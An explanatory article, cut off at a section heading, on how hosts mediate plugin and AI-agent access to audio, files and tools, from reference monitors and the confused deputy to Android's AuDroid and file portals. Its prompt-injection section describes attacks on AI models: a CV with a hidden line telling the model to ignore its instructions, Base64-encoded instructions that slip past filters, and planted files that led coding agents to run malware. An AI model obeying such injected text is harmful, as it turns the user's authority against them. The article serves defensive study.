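# Host-mediated access to audio, files and tools by plugins and AI agents

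## What it means for a host to mediate access

Host-mediated access is an arrangement in which outside code can use a microphone, a file or an online account only by sending a request through another program, the host. A photo-editing plugin requests a picture from its host and receives either the picture or an error. An AI agent told to "send Alice the photos from Saturday" also has to go through a host, but it works out during the task which folders to read, whether to shrink the files first, and which service to send them with.

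The host is the program or system component between a plugin or agent and the audio, files or tools it uses. A plugin is third-party code that runs with or inside a host. Its developer wrote its behaviour beforehand, so someone reading the source code can work out which requests it may make. An agent is an AI model that chooses and carries out actions to reach a goal set by a user. It acts mostly through tool calls, which are structured requests to run a named function with given arguments, such as a "send email" function with a recipient and an attachment. Many agents access tools through the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for connecting models to outside services.

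*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes the usual loop. An application sends the model the conversation and a description of the available tools. The model returns either an answer for the user or a tool call. If it returns a tool call, the application runs the function or declines to, adds the result to the conversation and queries the model again, until the model returns a final answer. The model only produces text, and other software opens the file or sends the email, so a host can intervene before that software acts.

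There are five things a host can do with a request:

- Refuse it: the photo plugin asks for the microphone, and the host returns an error.
- Narrow it: the plugin asks for the photo library, and the host hands over the one picture the user picked.
- Ask the user: before the agent emails anything to Alice, the host shows the files and the address and waits for a yes.
- Record it: the host logs which folder the agent opened, when, and for which task.
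- Label the data: the host marks the text of an incoming email as untrusted, and later checks take the mark into account.

Most hosts combine several of these. A log entry doesn't block an action, but David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, recommends logging tool calls in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* (2025) because attackers usually have to refine an attack, so failed calls can expose them early. A label also has no effect until a later check reads it. AuDroid, a research system for Android phones, applied labels to sound.

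### The reference monitor

The theory behind host-mediated access is much older than AI agents. Around 1970 the US Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972) reports an expert panel's view of the problem. The panel's concern was a legitimate user who writes and runs a hostile program. Keeping outsiders away doesn't stop someone who already has an account, so whatever controls running programs has to provide the protection.

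The panel proposed the reference monitor, a component that checks every attempt by a program to use data, a device or another program against a list of what the first program is allowed to do for its user. The list can be a table with a row for each user or program, a column for each file or device, and entries such as "read" or "write".

Anderson set three requirements for the monitor: nobody can tamper with it, it runs on every access, and it is small enough to analyse and test completely, because otherwise nobody can know that it works correctly in every case. He then checked a real system against them, the HIS 635 computer with its GCOS III operating system. The hardware acted as a kind of monitor by confining each user's program to its own area of memory. But programs called on the operating system for input and output, and most of the operating system ran with that confinement suspended.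 The operating system itself would fail the third requirement if it were treated as the monitor, because it had between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions, far too many to test completely. Several penetration exercises had already succeeded against it.

An AI model cannot meet the size requirement, because nobody can test one exhaustively. A model may still be useful for judging requests, but a host that relies on a model's judgement alone has no reference monitor in Anderson's sense.

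Three years later, Saltzer and Schroeder's *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* listed eight design principles for protection, two of which come up constantly in work on agents. Complete mediation means that the system checks every access to every protected object, including during start-up, recovery and maintenance. This requires a foolproof way to identify the source of each request. Reusing the result of an earlier check to save time is suspect, because somebody may have withdrawn the permission since. Least privilege means that each program runs with only the access its current job needs, so a photo plugin that needs one picture should not have access to the whole library. This limits the damage from a mistake and leaves fewer programs to examine after a misuse.

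### The confused deputy

A system can check every request and still allow a harmful one. In *The Confused Deputy*, Hardy (1988) tells a "nearly true story" from Tymshare, a company that rented out time on shared computers. Customers could give a compiler the name of a file to receive debugging output. The compiler also wrote usage statistics to a file in its own directory, SYSX, so Tymshare gave it a licence to write there. The billing records were in SYSX too. When one customer named the billing file as the destination for debugging output, the operating system found that the compiler had a licence for SYSX and let it write, and the billing information was lost.

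The check ran and applied its rules correctly. Hardy's explanation for the fault was that the compiler had authority from two sources, the customer and its own licence, and had no way to indicate which one a given write relied on. A confused deputy is a program with legitimate access that is tricked into using it on behalf of someone who lacks that access.

Checking file names inside the compiler would not have helped much. Customers had good reasons to send output to other directories, SYSX held other sensitive files, and the name SYSX did not exist when the programmer wrote the output code. Tymshare added a way for a program to switch between its two authorities, but soon found applications that needed more than two. Hardy preferred to use capabilities. Saltzer and Schroeder define a capability as an unforgeable ticket proving that its holder may use a particular object. The customer would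 give the compiler a ticket for an output file instead of a name, so a customer without a ticket for the billing file could not direct output to it.

Agents can fail in the same way with no attacker's text involved. *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security* (2026) gives the example of an employee who asks a company's agent for everyone's salary. The employee has no access to the personnel database, but the agent does, for administrative work. If $R$ is the set of permitted pairs of subject and resource, the trouble arises when

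$$(\text{user}, \text{database}) \notin R \quad \text{but} \quad (\text{agent}, \text{database}) \in R.$$

A host has to check the permissions of the person an agent is acting for. If it checks only the agent's permissions, it can let through queries that the person isn't allowed to make.

### Labels for secrecy and integrity

An ordinary access check ends when the program gets the file. Information-flow control governs what happens to the contents afterwards. It uses labels, which record how secret or trustworthy something is, to determine where data may go and what it may influence.

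Suppose each piece of data is marked secret or public, and trusted or untrusted. An assistant can read a payroll file, which is secret and trusted, and a web page, which is public and untrusted. Under the secrecy rule, secret data must not reach an untrusted party, so the host blocks an email carrying payroll figures to an outside address, even though the assistant may read the file and may send email. Under the integrity rule, untrusted data must not influence a trusted action, so text from the web page can appear in a summary but cannot determine who receives the payroll report. Data that combines the two sources takes the more restrictive mark for both secrecy and integrity, so a paragraph drawn from both is secret and untrusted.

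The secrecy half comes from military classification. MITRE's *Integrity Considerations for Secure Computer Systems* (1977), a report by Kenneth Biba, restates it as two conditions. A subject $s$ may read an object $o$ only if $\text{level}(o) \le \text{level}(s)$, and may write to it only if $\text{level}(s) \le \text{level}(o)$, so information can move only upward in secrecy. Biba's own subject was integrity, by which he meant that a subsystem can be trusted to keep to a defined code of behaviour, whatever the merits of that code. He compared direct attempts to corrupt a subsystem to a knife, and indirect ones to poison slipped into food. An indirect attacker doesn't need access to the victim's files if the victim takes in bad data.

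Strict labels can severely limit what an agent can do. In the simplest design that Costa and colleagues model, one untrusted email makes the whole conversation untrusted. A host that requires trusted input for consequential actions would then refuse every such action. Practical systems therefore need exceptions. Declassification permits the release of some secret data, and endorsement permits some untrusted data to influence a protected decision. The system's guarantees then depend on how sound the rules for granting these exceptions are.

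### Prompt injection

Prompt injection is text in a web page, file or tool result that an agent wrongly treats as an instruction. David C describes a recruiter's system that asks a model to score CVs. A candidate hides a line in the CV telling the model to ignore its instructions and approve the candidate for interview, and the model may do so. This is an *indirect* prompt injection because the candidate never had access to the system and only wrote text that it would later process.

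The weakness arises because these systems combine the developer's instructions, the user's request and the results of tool calls into one text. Developers put separators between the parts, but *The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents* (2026) explains that the model processes everything as a single sequence, and untrusted text can imitate trusted text. David C contrasts this with SQL injection, in which an attacker types database commands into a form field. Programmers can prevent this by passing the field's contents separately, so that the database never interprets them as a command. A language model has no such separate channel. It predicts the next piece of text from everything before it, and he thinks a complete fix may never come.

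Developers can train models to give priority to trusted instructions, or mark outside text as data. *Trustworthy Agentic AI* (2026) concludes that these defences reduce the risk but do not remove it. Filters that look for known phrases are weaker because an attacker can rephrase. In *Not what you've signed up for*, Greshake and colleagues (2023) got an instruction through by encoding it in Base64, which turns text into a string that looks unreadable, and having the model decode it.

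Current agents still fall for this. In a harmless test described in *The Attack That Arrived as a Footnote*, Howard (2026) gave Claude and Codex an algebra quiz PDF with five visible questions and a sixth hidden in its text. Both assistants noticed something odd about the document but solved the sixth problem anyway. Attackers are trying it too. Mascellino (2026), in *Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails*, reports that the security company Barracuda found phishing emails written to manipulate AI assistants as well as people. TechRadar's *AI agents tricked by a rogue downloads file into running dangerous malware* describes an instruction file that researchers found planted in a customer's Downloads folder. When they reproduced the attack, it worked on two coding agents. These cases don't show how often such attacks succeed. In an older benchmark cited in *Trustworthy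 Agentic AI*, attacks on an agent built on GPT-4, a model from 2023, succeeded about one time in four.

Prompt injection turns an agent into a confused deputy. The agent holds the user's authority over mail, files and accounts, and injected text can make it use that authority for whoever wrote the text. Hardy's compiler could be fixed because its programmers could separate the two authorities in code. David C calls language models "inherently confusable" because nobody can make that separation reliably inside the model. He advises putting the limits in ordinary software around the model and planning for an attacker who can directly use every tool the agent can call. He also cites a rule from an exchange between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista that when a model processes text from some party, its privileges drop to that party's. An agent reading email from strangers would then have only the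 tools a stranger should have. The rule is safe, but it would also block some legitimate tasks, such as sending Alice her photos when the agent has to open a stranger's email to find her address.

### What makes agents hard to authorise

The developer of a plugin specifies in code which functions the plugin can call, whereas an agent chooses its sequence of actions as it runs, based on text that mixes instructions with whatever it has found. The survey *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (Zhou and Zhang, November 2026) derives three difficulties from this. It distinguishes a grant, which is the part of a user's authority that an agent receives for a task under stated conditions, from an approval, which is a person's explicit agreement to one sensitive operation or to a wider grant.

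The user grants access before the agent's plan is complete. An agent asked to write a report from approved records, for example, could analyse them on the user's own machine or send them to an outside analysis service. Both plans may give an equally good report, but the second discloses the records to another company. If the host grants only the minimum permissions for the second plan, it still grants more than the task needs. Least privilege therefore has to begin with the choice of plan. If $\Pi$ is the set of plans that would do the job well enough, $A(\pi)$ the permissions that plan $\pi$ requires and $G$ the current grant, the agent should look for a $\pi \in \Pi$ with $A(\pi) \subseteq G$ before anyone asks the user for more permissions.

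Information can also influence a decision without authorising it. Suppose the grant lets the agent send the report to a partner company's contact, and a trusted directory identifies that contact as Alice. A document the agent retrieves contains an instruction to copy in Bob. Both are relevant to the task, but the directory identifies a recipient the user has already allowed, while the instruction would add a new one. Restricting a source to short answers does not solve this, because a single "yes" to the question of whether a draft may leave the organisation is enough to release a confidential file. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) points out that a tool's output can influence a decision without justifying it, so even a good log does not settle afterwards whether the decision was authorised.

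The third difficulty is that effects can outlast an approval. A queued message may go out after the user has changed their mind. An agent with permission to buy one item may pass the job to two other agents, each with permission to buy one, and two items arrive although neither agent broke its limit. After a timeout, an agent may not know whether its order went through, and trying again may buy a second item. Conventional systems handle this by reserving the item in one indivisible step and giving every attempt the same identifier, so that the seller's system can recognise a repeat. Zhou and Zhang note that an agent can inadvertently defeat this safeguard if it responds to the timeout by making a new plan, with different arguments or a different tool, because the repeat then looks like a new order. Withdrawing the grant blocks further attempts, but it does not cancel an order the seller already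 has or recall a report Alice has already received.

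## Labelled audio on Android phones

A phone app with microphone access can record the phone's own speaker as well as the people in the room. On Android phones in 2015, such an app could hear a screen reader speak the owner's password. Playing sound needed no permission, so any app could also play a spoken command to the phone's voice assistant. Checking each request separately does not reveal the problem, because one program is allowed to play sound and the other is allowed to listen, and the harm comes from sound passing between them.

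*AuDroid* (Petracca, Sun and colleagues, 2016) describes a modified version of Android 5.0.1 that controls audio channels. It puts secrecy and integrity labels on every party to a channel and checks each channel before it opens. Android is the host, and the phone's apps are the plugins.

### Why the check sits in the media server

An Android app records sound by calling a function in Android's programming interface. The request goes to the Media Server, a system process that opens the microphone and passes the sound back. SELinux, the access-control system in Android's kernel, allows only the Media Server to open the device files for the microphone and speaker, so every app's audio must pass through it.

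Petracca and colleagues put their checks inside the Media Server because it still has the identity of the calling app. Although the kernel sits below everything else, a check there could not distinguish a voice recorder from the voice assistant, because the requests it receives come from the Media Server, whichever app started them. This problem is much like the one with Hardy's compiler.

AuDroid uses four hooks, which are points where the normal code calls AuDroid. Two run when a program starts using the microphone or the speaker, and two run when it stops. AuDroid needs the stop hooks because a channel exists only while both ends are active. In a test of complete mediation on the running system, a hook fired on every access to either device. This is good evidence for the paths that the test exercised, but an untested path could still bypass the hooks.

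### Three channels and six attacks

A phone's speaker and microphone can form three kinds of channel: from the speaker to the microphone, from the speaker to an outside party, and from an outside party to the microphone. An outside party is any person or device within earshot, including the owner. Each channel allows one eavesdropping attack and one confused-deputy attack.

| Channel | Eavesdropping | Confused deputy |
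|---|---|---|
| Speaker to microphone | A hostile app records the screen reader speaking a password | A hostile app plays a command to the phone's assistant |
| Speaker to outside party | A hostile app plays back recorded secrets to an accomplice after the owner has walked away | A hostile app plays a command to another phone, a thermostat or a car |
| Outside party to microphone | A hostile app records the owner's conversations | A stranger speaks a command to the phone |

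Other researchers had already demonstrated several of these attacks. One group's app started Google Voice Search and gave it spoken commands, and another group's app extracted credit card numbers from recorded audio. Petracca and colleagues wrote apps that carried out the two attacks on the channel from the phone's speaker to outsiders.

One attack can also enable another. Android accepted a spoken command to turn on "Speak Passwords" in the accessibility settings. A hostile app could play that command and later record the spoken passwords.

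### From a microphone request to a decision

Suppose an app asks to record a voice message. AuDroid handles the request in five steps:

1. Android checks that the app has permission to use the microphone, as it did before AuDroid.
2. The hook reads the caller's process number, and AuDroid looks up the caller's labels. System apps and services, which come with the phone, have high secrecy and high integrity. Market apps, which the owner installs, have low secrecy and low integrity.
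3. AuDroid works out which channels the request would open. A microphone request can open one from whatever program is using the speaker and another from anyone within earshot.
4. It labels the outside party.
5. It applies the flow rules to each channel. If every flow is safe, the recording starts. If not, AuDroid looks for a permitted exception, and without one it refuses the request.

AuDroid labels the outside party cautiously, according to the direction of the sound. Someone listening to the phone's speaker gets low secrecy, because they could be anyone and the phone should not play them secrets, and high integrity, because they might be misled. Someone talking into the microphone gets high secrecy, because they could be the owner saying something private, and low integrity, because they could be a stranger giving orders. Once the owner has unlocked the screen, AuDroid gives the outside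 party high secrecy and high integrity in both directions.

The flow rules are the two from the previous section. Write $S(p)$ for a party's secrecy and $I(p)$ for its integrity, with 1 for high and 0 for low. Sound may flow from $a$ to $b$ only if

$$S(a) \le S(b) \quad \text{and} \quad I(a) \ge I(b).$$

Any two market apps have equal labels, so these conditions alone would let one record the other. To prevent this, AuDroid also puts market apps into separate categories and blocks sound between them.

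A game might try to play "send an email to Kristin" while the assistant is listening. The game has $S = 0$ and $I = 0$, and the assistant has $S = 1$ and $I = 1$. The secrecy condition holds because $0 \le 1$, but the integrity condition fails because it requires $0 \ge 1$. AuDroid therefore blocks the game from using the speaker. Base Android had no check on the speaker, so it would have let the command through.

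A market app may request to record the owner while the screen is unlocked. The sound would flow from the owner, with $S = 1$ and $I = 1$, to an app with $S = 0$ and $I = 0$, so the integrity condition holds but the secrecy condition fails. Refusing every such request would make voice recorders useless, so AuDroid asks the owner whether to allow the recording.

### Resolvers and the owner's approval

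Applied strictly, the rules would make a phone nearly useless. When a locked phone rings, a system app plays sound to an unknown listener, which breaks the secrecy rule. When Spotify plays a song, a low-integrity app sends sound to a high-integrity owner, which breaks the integrity rule.

When a flow breaks a rule, AuDroid proposes a resolver, a known method for making an unsafe flow acceptable, to the system app or service at risk. The sound flows only if that app or service accepts. The AuDroid paper tests two resolvers. One lets system apps play approved ringtones and notification sounds when the screen is locked, a form of declassification. The other lets market apps play approved audio files to a high-integrity listener, a form of endorsement. The game's recorded command is not an approved file, so it stays blocked.

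The second resolver is only as reliable as the approval it depends on. Checking a ringtone stored on the phone is fairly easy. Checking everything Spotify might stream is much harder, and checking live speech is harder still. The AuDroid paper reports running a Skype video call under the system, but nobody can approve a caller's words in advance.

No system app can decide on the owner's behalf whether a market app may record the owner. AuDroid therefore asks the owner through a trusted prompt, which the system displays and the app cannot alter. The prompt names the parties that the channel would connect, and recording doesn't start until the owner agrees. The idea comes from user-driven access control, but AuDroid triggers the prompt from the Media Server, so it doesn't depend on app developers to include it.

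When the owner approves a flow, AuDroid changes the outside party's label for that channel but not the policy. In the recording example, the flow can pass only if AuDroid lowers the owner's secrecy from 1 to 0, which treats the speech as public on this channel. The rule against sending secret sound to a market app still applies to every other app. AuDroid keeps a short-lived record of recent decisions so that an identical flow moments later doesn't trigger another prompt, a kind of shortcut that Saltzer and Schroeder distrusted.

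AuDroid's control ends once an app has the recording. Its labels apply to the parties on an audio channel and do not follow the sound into a file or across the internet. Systems that label an agent's data try to control what happens to the data after the agent receives it.

### What the tests found

AuDroid prevented all six types of attack in a comparison by Petracca and colleagues. Unmodified Android stopped none, and five other defences stopped at most two each. Banning two programs from using the microphone and speaker at the same time stops both attacks from speaker to microphone, but has no effect on attacks that involve outsiders. Voiceprint recognition can stop commands from a stranger or a hostile app, unless the attacker replays a recording of the owner.

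The authors also ran 17 widely used apps, and all of them worked. The results for the flow rules alone show how much of this depended on the exceptions:

| Apps | Rules broken without exceptions | What allowed them to run |
|---|---|---|
| Five system apps, including Music, Voice Search and Maps | None | Nothing needed |
| Phone and Hangouts | Secrecy | Approved ringtones and notification sounds |
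| Pandora and Spotify | Integrity | Approved audio files |
| Eight market apps, including WhatsApp, Skype and Voice Recorder | Secrecy and integrity | Approved audio files and the owner's approval |

All ten market apps broke at least one rule. So for apps that people install themselves, AuDroid's security depends mostly on the file approvals and the owner's answers, and the flow rules mainly determine when AuDroid asks for them.

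AuDroid added very little delay. The paper's introduction gives the added delay as under 4 microseconds for the speaker and under 25 for the microphone. The averages over 10,000 requests are about 4.1 microseconds for the speaker and 4.8 for the microphone, or 13.1 with the visual notification. The speaker average is slightly above the stated limit, but the difference doesn't matter in practice. A sequence of 11 apps took 591 seconds on average both with and without AuDroid.

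### What AuDroid takes for granted

AuDroid assumes that the operating system and all the software that came with the phone are not malicious and can protect themselves. That assumption was weak for the Media Server of the time. The server also handled video, and Google (2016) explained that an attacker who exploited a bug in its media library, libstagefright, gained all of the server's permissions. An attacker inside the Media Server could have accessed the microphone directly, without triggering a hook. AuDroid's own code was under 800 lines, but Anderson's size requirement applies to everything the monitor depends on.

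Android 7.0 split up the Media Server. According to the Android Open Source Project's *Media framework hardening*, audio input and output moved to a separate process called AudioServer, and many of the decoders for media files moved to another process with few permissions. A modern version of AuDroid would presumably put its hooks in AudioServer, so a bug in one of those decoders would no longer give an attacker control of its check.

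AuDroid's method of identifying callers is also unreliable. It treats processes numbered up to 2,000 as system processes and those with higher numbers as market apps. But Linux numbers processes in the order they start and eventually reuses old numbers, so a market app could get a number in the system's range and receive high integrity. The Android Open Source Project's *Android permissions for system developers* describes a better identifier, the uid, which Android usually assigns to each app at installation. Using the uid would be a small change, but without it AuDroid lacks the foolproof identification that complete mediation requires.

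Screen unlock is weak proof that the owner is speaking. While the phone is unlocked, AuDroid gives high integrity to anyone within earshot, so a stranger or a television can give the assistant commands. It also treats the owner as a stranger when they call out to a locked phone. The AuDroid paper leaves better authentication to future work.

AuDroid also relies on people noticing when the microphone is on. It shows an icon while a program is recording, or a blinking light if the screen is off, and leaves it to the owner to avoid private subjects until the recording ends. In support, Petracca and colleagues cite a user study in which visual notifications caught people's attention in 64–77% of cases. That study tested security badges rather than microphone notifications. Participants used an emulated phone and had to notice when a fake Facebook app opened with the badge missing or showing the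 wrong picture. They had chosen the correct picture themselves shortly before, and the researchers asked them after each task whether the app was genuine.

A more direct test gave a much worse result. In *An Empirical Study on the Effectiveness of Privacy Indicators*, Guerra, Scalabrino and colleagues (2023) recruited 122 Android users and taught them about the microphone indicator that Android had since introduced. In one task, a simulated Spotify app used the microphone for no good reason while participants looked for a song. The indicator was on screen for 57 participants, and two noticed it. Only four of the other 55 found it when they looked at screenshots afterwards. During a voice call, 74.6% of people with the indicator reported that the app had used the microphone, compared with 61.4% of those without it, a difference that was not statistically significant.

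Most of the participants were aged 18 to 24 and the apps were imitations, so the exact rate may not hold elsewhere. Still, two in 57, or about 4%, is far below 64%. In *Visual Attention and Privacy Indicators in Android*, Guerra, Milanese and colleagues tracked the eyes of 29 students and found that they often missed the standard indicator, especially during games. A more prominent design did significantly better in Guerra and colleagues' follow-up with 38 people. On this evidence, AuDroid's prompt, which stops the recording until the owner answers, gives much more protection than its icon.

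### What Android controls today

On the Android version that AuDroid modified, an app received microphone permission automatically at installation. Google's *Request runtime permissions* explains that apps have had to ask during use since Android 6.0, and that since Android 11 the owner can choose "Only this time". This one-time permission lasts while the app is visible and for a short period afterwards. It can last longer if the app started a foreground service, a task that keeps running behind other apps and shows a notification. If the owner withdraws the permission, Android shuts the app down. Android also resets permissions for many apps that nobody has used for a few months.

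A one-time permission is similar to AuDroid's approval, but it applies to the app rather than to a channel. Android's dialog shows the permission the app is requesting, while AuDroid's prompt also shows which parties the channel would connect. While the permission lasts, the app can record whatever reaches the microphone, subject to the rules on sharing the microphone.

Android 12 introduced the microphone indicator. According to the Android Open Source Project's *Privacy indicators*, Android records each use of the microphone and, if the app is not part of the system, shows an icon that then shrinks to a dot. Tapping the indicator shows which apps are using the microphone or did so in the last 15 seconds. Phone calls use separate microphone software, which has to report its own use. AuDroid's icon also appeared for system apps.

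Supported phones also have a switch that cuts off the microphone for every app. According to Google's *Explain access to more sensitive information*, apps receive silence while the microphone is off, and Android slows down motion sensor readings. This is probably because fast readings can pick up vibrations from speech, which would give an app another way to listen.

The closest thing to AuDroid's labels is Android's rules for apps that record at the same time. Until Android 10, the first app to start recording usually kept the microphone to itself. Google's *Sharing audio input* describes the order of priority that replaced this. Two ordinary apps never receive sound together. An app recording from a privacy-sensitive source, such as a voice call, takes priority over one that isn't. Otherwise, the app on top of the screen has priority. The other app keeps running but receives silence. The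 Android Open Source Project's *Concurrent capture* explains that Android silences the app instead of refusing it so that it can get the sound back once the other has finished. According to the project's *Audio recording*, makers of devices with a microphone must follow these rules.

Android makes an exception for preinstalled assistants, which can listen while an ordinary app records unless that app is using a privacy-sensitive source. In return, Android Open Source Project guidance requires that microphone data stay on the device until the user interacts with the assistant, for example by saying its trigger word. This requirement governs how the assistant's developer handles the data, and the silencing rules can't enforce it. According to Google, Android 17 adds a separate permission for recording during calls and in other sensitive situations.

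Android has much less control over the speaker. Since Android 10, an app can copy another app's sound inside the phone if the user allows it, but the developer of the app playing the sound can forbid this (Turner, 2019). This is a little like a secrecy label, but it covers only the internal copy, not what a microphone picks up. Android 17 also stops apps from playing sound in the background unless they run a foreground service. Google's *Background audio hardening* says this is meant to prevent unintended sounds, such as when an app resumes playing hours later.

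None of these controls compares the program playing a sound with the one listening. They also have no equivalent of AuDroid's resolvers or its labels for people and devices outside the phone. A game open on the screen can still play "send an email to Kristin" through the speaker, and whether the email is sent depends on the assistant's own checks.

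## File and camera access granted by the user's own action

AuDroid took the idea for its trusted prompt from *User-Driven Access Control* (Roesner, Kohno and colleagues, 2012), which proposed a design meant to make most prompts unnecessary. The operating system draws the camera button inside an app, and the user grants access by pressing it. The app receives one photo and cannot use the camera before or after the press. The user doesn't have to answer a prompt.

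### The trouble with manifests and prompts

A manifest is a list of the permissions an app requests, which the user accepts at installation. Android used manifests in 2012. The user had to decide before seeing the app do anything, and the app could then use the camera at any time. Roesner and colleagues cite studies which found that many apps requested more permissions than they needed, and that users paid little attention to the lists and understood little of them. Roesner and colleagues would keep manifests only as a way for developers to privately tell the system the most access an app will ever need. The system could then hold the app to that limit if an attacker took it over.

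Prompts come at a better moment than manifests, but users learn to click through them, because someone who has just pressed "take photo" sees no point in being asked whether the app may use the camera. The iPhone reduced the annoyance by asking only the first time an app requested a resource, which made the answer nearly as permanent as a manifest.

In 2024, browser developers were still struggling with permission prompts. The session minutes in W3C's *Page Embedded Permission Control* describe users who no longer notice prompts and decisions that few people manage to reverse. When browsers made prompts less intrusive, fewer people granted access, and some didn't get the feature they wanted. Requiring a click somewhere on the page before a prompt wasn't "much of a filter" either. Roesner and colleagues had criticized Flash for this in 2012, because people click for many reasons unrelated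 to permissions.

They trace both problems to the operating system's inability to detect what the user is doing inside the app, which means it has to prompt the user for permission. For example, it can't distinguish an ordinary camera button from the other pixels the app draws.

### From the button to the photo

Their replacement is the access control gadget, a button or other control that the system supplies and the app embeds in its own window. For a single photo it works like this:

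1. The app requests a "take picture" gadget at a certain position. It can set a few properties, such as colour and size, from fixed lists.
2. The camera's resource monitor draws the gadget. This is a privileged program that provides the only route to the camera, and each type of resource has its own. The app cannot change the gadget's pixels.
3. The kernel, the core of the operating system, checks that the gadget is opaque, fully visible and in front of everything else. It activates the gadget only after 200 milliseconds in the same place. Without that delay, an app could make the gadget appear just as the user was about to press something else.
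4. The user presses the gadget. The kernel accepts input only from physical devices such as the touchscreen, so an app can't fake a press.
5. The kernel works out which app should benefit. An advertisement inside a news site might embed a location gadget and imitate the site's design, so by default only the outermost app can embed active gadgets.
6. The monitor takes the picture, and the kernel passes it to the app.

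The app never calls the camera itself. If it could, it might delay the photo until the camera was pointing at something else. Counterfeit gadgets are a smaller worry because, although an app can draw its own camera button, pressing that button grants no access.

Some jobs need longer access:

| Duration | Example | How access ends |
|---|---|---|
| One-time | Taking a photo | The app has received one item |
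| Session | Navigating with a map | The user stops it or closes the app |
| Scheduled | Backing up files every 12 hours | The user changes the schedule or withdraws the grant |
| Permanent | Receiving every text message | The user withdraws the grant |

In the first two rows, the user's actions mark when access begins and ends. In the other two, the system relies only on the user's earlier choice. The paper proposes a gadget for setting schedules, and suggests requiring extra confirmation for permanent access to discourage developers from requesting it.

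Keyboard shortcuts and gestures can also grant access. Pressing Ctrl-V gives an app the contents of the clipboard once. The design also allows a spoken "Take a picture" to grant camera access, although the prototype implemented only clipboard shortcuts and drag-and-drop. The attacks described in AuDroid suggest that the spoken version would be unsafe, because an app could play the command aloud.

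### How much it would cover

Roesner and colleagues reviewed 631 known security flaws in Chrome and Firefox and found 70 that concerned access to the user's own resources. They judged that their design would prevent 61 of these, 36 of 44 in Chrome (82%) and 25 of 26 in Firefox (96%). Those percentages are the paper's headline figures, but the design would prevent only about one in ten of all 631 flaws. Most of the others were memory errors and other ways around the isolation between websites, which a gadget does not address. Of the nine relevant flaws the design would not prevent, seven involved hostile content that users themselves moved into a vulnerable app, for example by pasting it.

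The paper's survey of 100 popular Android apps from November 2011 also found 143 uses of resources such as the camera, location and contacts. In 89 cases, the app needed access only in direct response to a user action. Another 23 needed scheduled or permanent access, 11 served purposes such as advertising, and the researchers could not identify a purpose for the other 20. Gadgets tied to a user's action would have been enough for the proper functions of 91 apps. The paper's figure of 95 also counts apps that could switch to scheduled access, or display the system's calendar instead of reading its contents, so it assumes that developers would redesign those apps.

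Two online surveys asked what people expected. In the first, just over 40% of the 139 participants wrongly believed that an app could read the clipboard only when they pasted, which was the most common answer. The second showed 186 people screenshots of real apps. Most said that an app should not have access to the camera, location or text messaging before they pressed the relevant button. Most also believed that apps couldn't use the camera or send texts before then, but most knew that apps could already get their location. Asked about an app that texts people after a missed call, 62% wrongly thought Android let it send messages only in that situation, and 74% thought that this should be the rule. Men made up 154 of the 186 participants, so the percentages may not hold for the general public.

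The first survey also included an experiment on whether the app or the system should draw the button. An earlier system let apps draw their own copy and paste buttons and displayed each button's true function beside the cursor. When a button's appearance didn't match that text, participants fell for the false button in 87% of trials. Most didn't notice the text, and mentioning it in the instructions made no significant difference. Android's microphone indicator failed in much the same way, and both results favour controls that people have to use over indicators they have to notice.

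An app can still use a genuine gadget to trick people. A hostile game could use location gadgets as the circles in tic-tac-toe, or tell players to press Ctrl-V to win. The paper argues that such a trick is at least clear evidence of bad intent, for which the developer could face legal action. It does not test how many people would fall for the trick.

### Opening one photo

Before the 2012 paper, two research desktops, CapDesk and Polaris, already gave an app only the files its user picked, and Mac OS X Lion and Windows 8 had adopted similar file pickers. On Linux, Flatpak packages many apps, each in a sandbox. These apps get files from outside the sandbox through portals, system services built to be safe for untrusted apps to call. GNOME's *Flatpak* (2018) explains that people dismiss yes-or-no questions without much thought, so the portal shows a file picker instead, and the user grants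 access by choosing a file.

Suppose a photo editor wants to open beach.jpg:

1. The editor calls the portal's OpenFile function. According to Flatpak's *Portal API Reference*, it can supply a title for the window and a filter, such as image files only.
2. The system shows the picker outside the editor's sandbox, so the user can look through every folder without revealing their contents to the editor.
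3. The user selects beach.jpg. The portal records the file and the editor's permissions for it. If the user cancels, the editor gets no file.
4. The editor receives an address such as /run/user/1000/doc/b9b41fb7/beach.jpg. This leads to a special directory that, inside the sandbox, contains only the files the editor is allowed to use.

The document portal can give an app permission to read a file, write to it, delete the portal's entry for it, and pass access to other apps. According to Flatpak's *Document portal*, recent versions also let an app with read permission look up the file's real location, so the app may learn the name of the folder.

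On a Mac, the picker also runs in a separate process. Mothers Ruin's *URL Bookmarks and Security-scoping*, which is based on reverse engineering, describes how the picker gives the editor access to a file. The picker's service, which can open all of the user's files, requests a token from the kernel that names beach.jpg and specifies whether the editor may write to it. The service then passes the token to the editor. The kernel accepts the token only if it carries a valid code made with a secret key, so the editor can't alter it to name a different file. The token is close to the unforgeable ticket that Hardy wanted for Tymshare's compiler.

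The token stops working when the Mac restarts. To keep access for longer, an app can save a bookmark. A system service later exchanges the bookmark for a new token after checking that the request comes from the same app and user. Until March 2025, any app could read the key used for these bookmarks if the user entered a password at a prompt. Apple then moved the key to stricter storage to fix a security flaw.

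Users can also grant access to whole folders, both on a Mac and through newer Linux portals. If the user picks a folder on a Mac, the app gains access to the files in it and in every folder below it, according to Apple's *Accessing files from the macOS App Sandbox*. Someone who chooses the Pictures folder instead of beach.jpg may give the app access to years of photos.

An app sometimes needs access to more than the one file the user picked. An image converter that opens beach.jpg doesn't automatically get permission to save a converted copy beside it. Apple lets developers declare related file types in advance for such cases. File pickers also don't suit an app that manages a whole music collection. GNOME's *Content and Device Access* treats collections, cameras and microphones as a separate problem, and its tentative design for them includes access dialogs.

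When the user opens beach.jpg, the Linux host receives the editor's identity, the window title, the filter and the user's choice. The host can later list which apps have access to the file and withdraw that access. It has no reliable information about why the editor requested the photo, because the editor's developer wrote the title. It also cannot stop the editor from keeping a copy, or from uploading the photo if the sandbox allows network access. Withdrawing access does not affect copies. Roesner and colleagues leave this problem to information-flow control.

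The grant can also last longer than the user expects. The portal can record a file for one session or permanently, and the user's choice of a file doesn't specify which. In the Fedora forum thread *Permission for individual files appearing in Flatpak permissions?*, one user describes a long list of old grants, many for files that no longer exist, and shares a script for clearing them.

### Buttons in Chrome and Android

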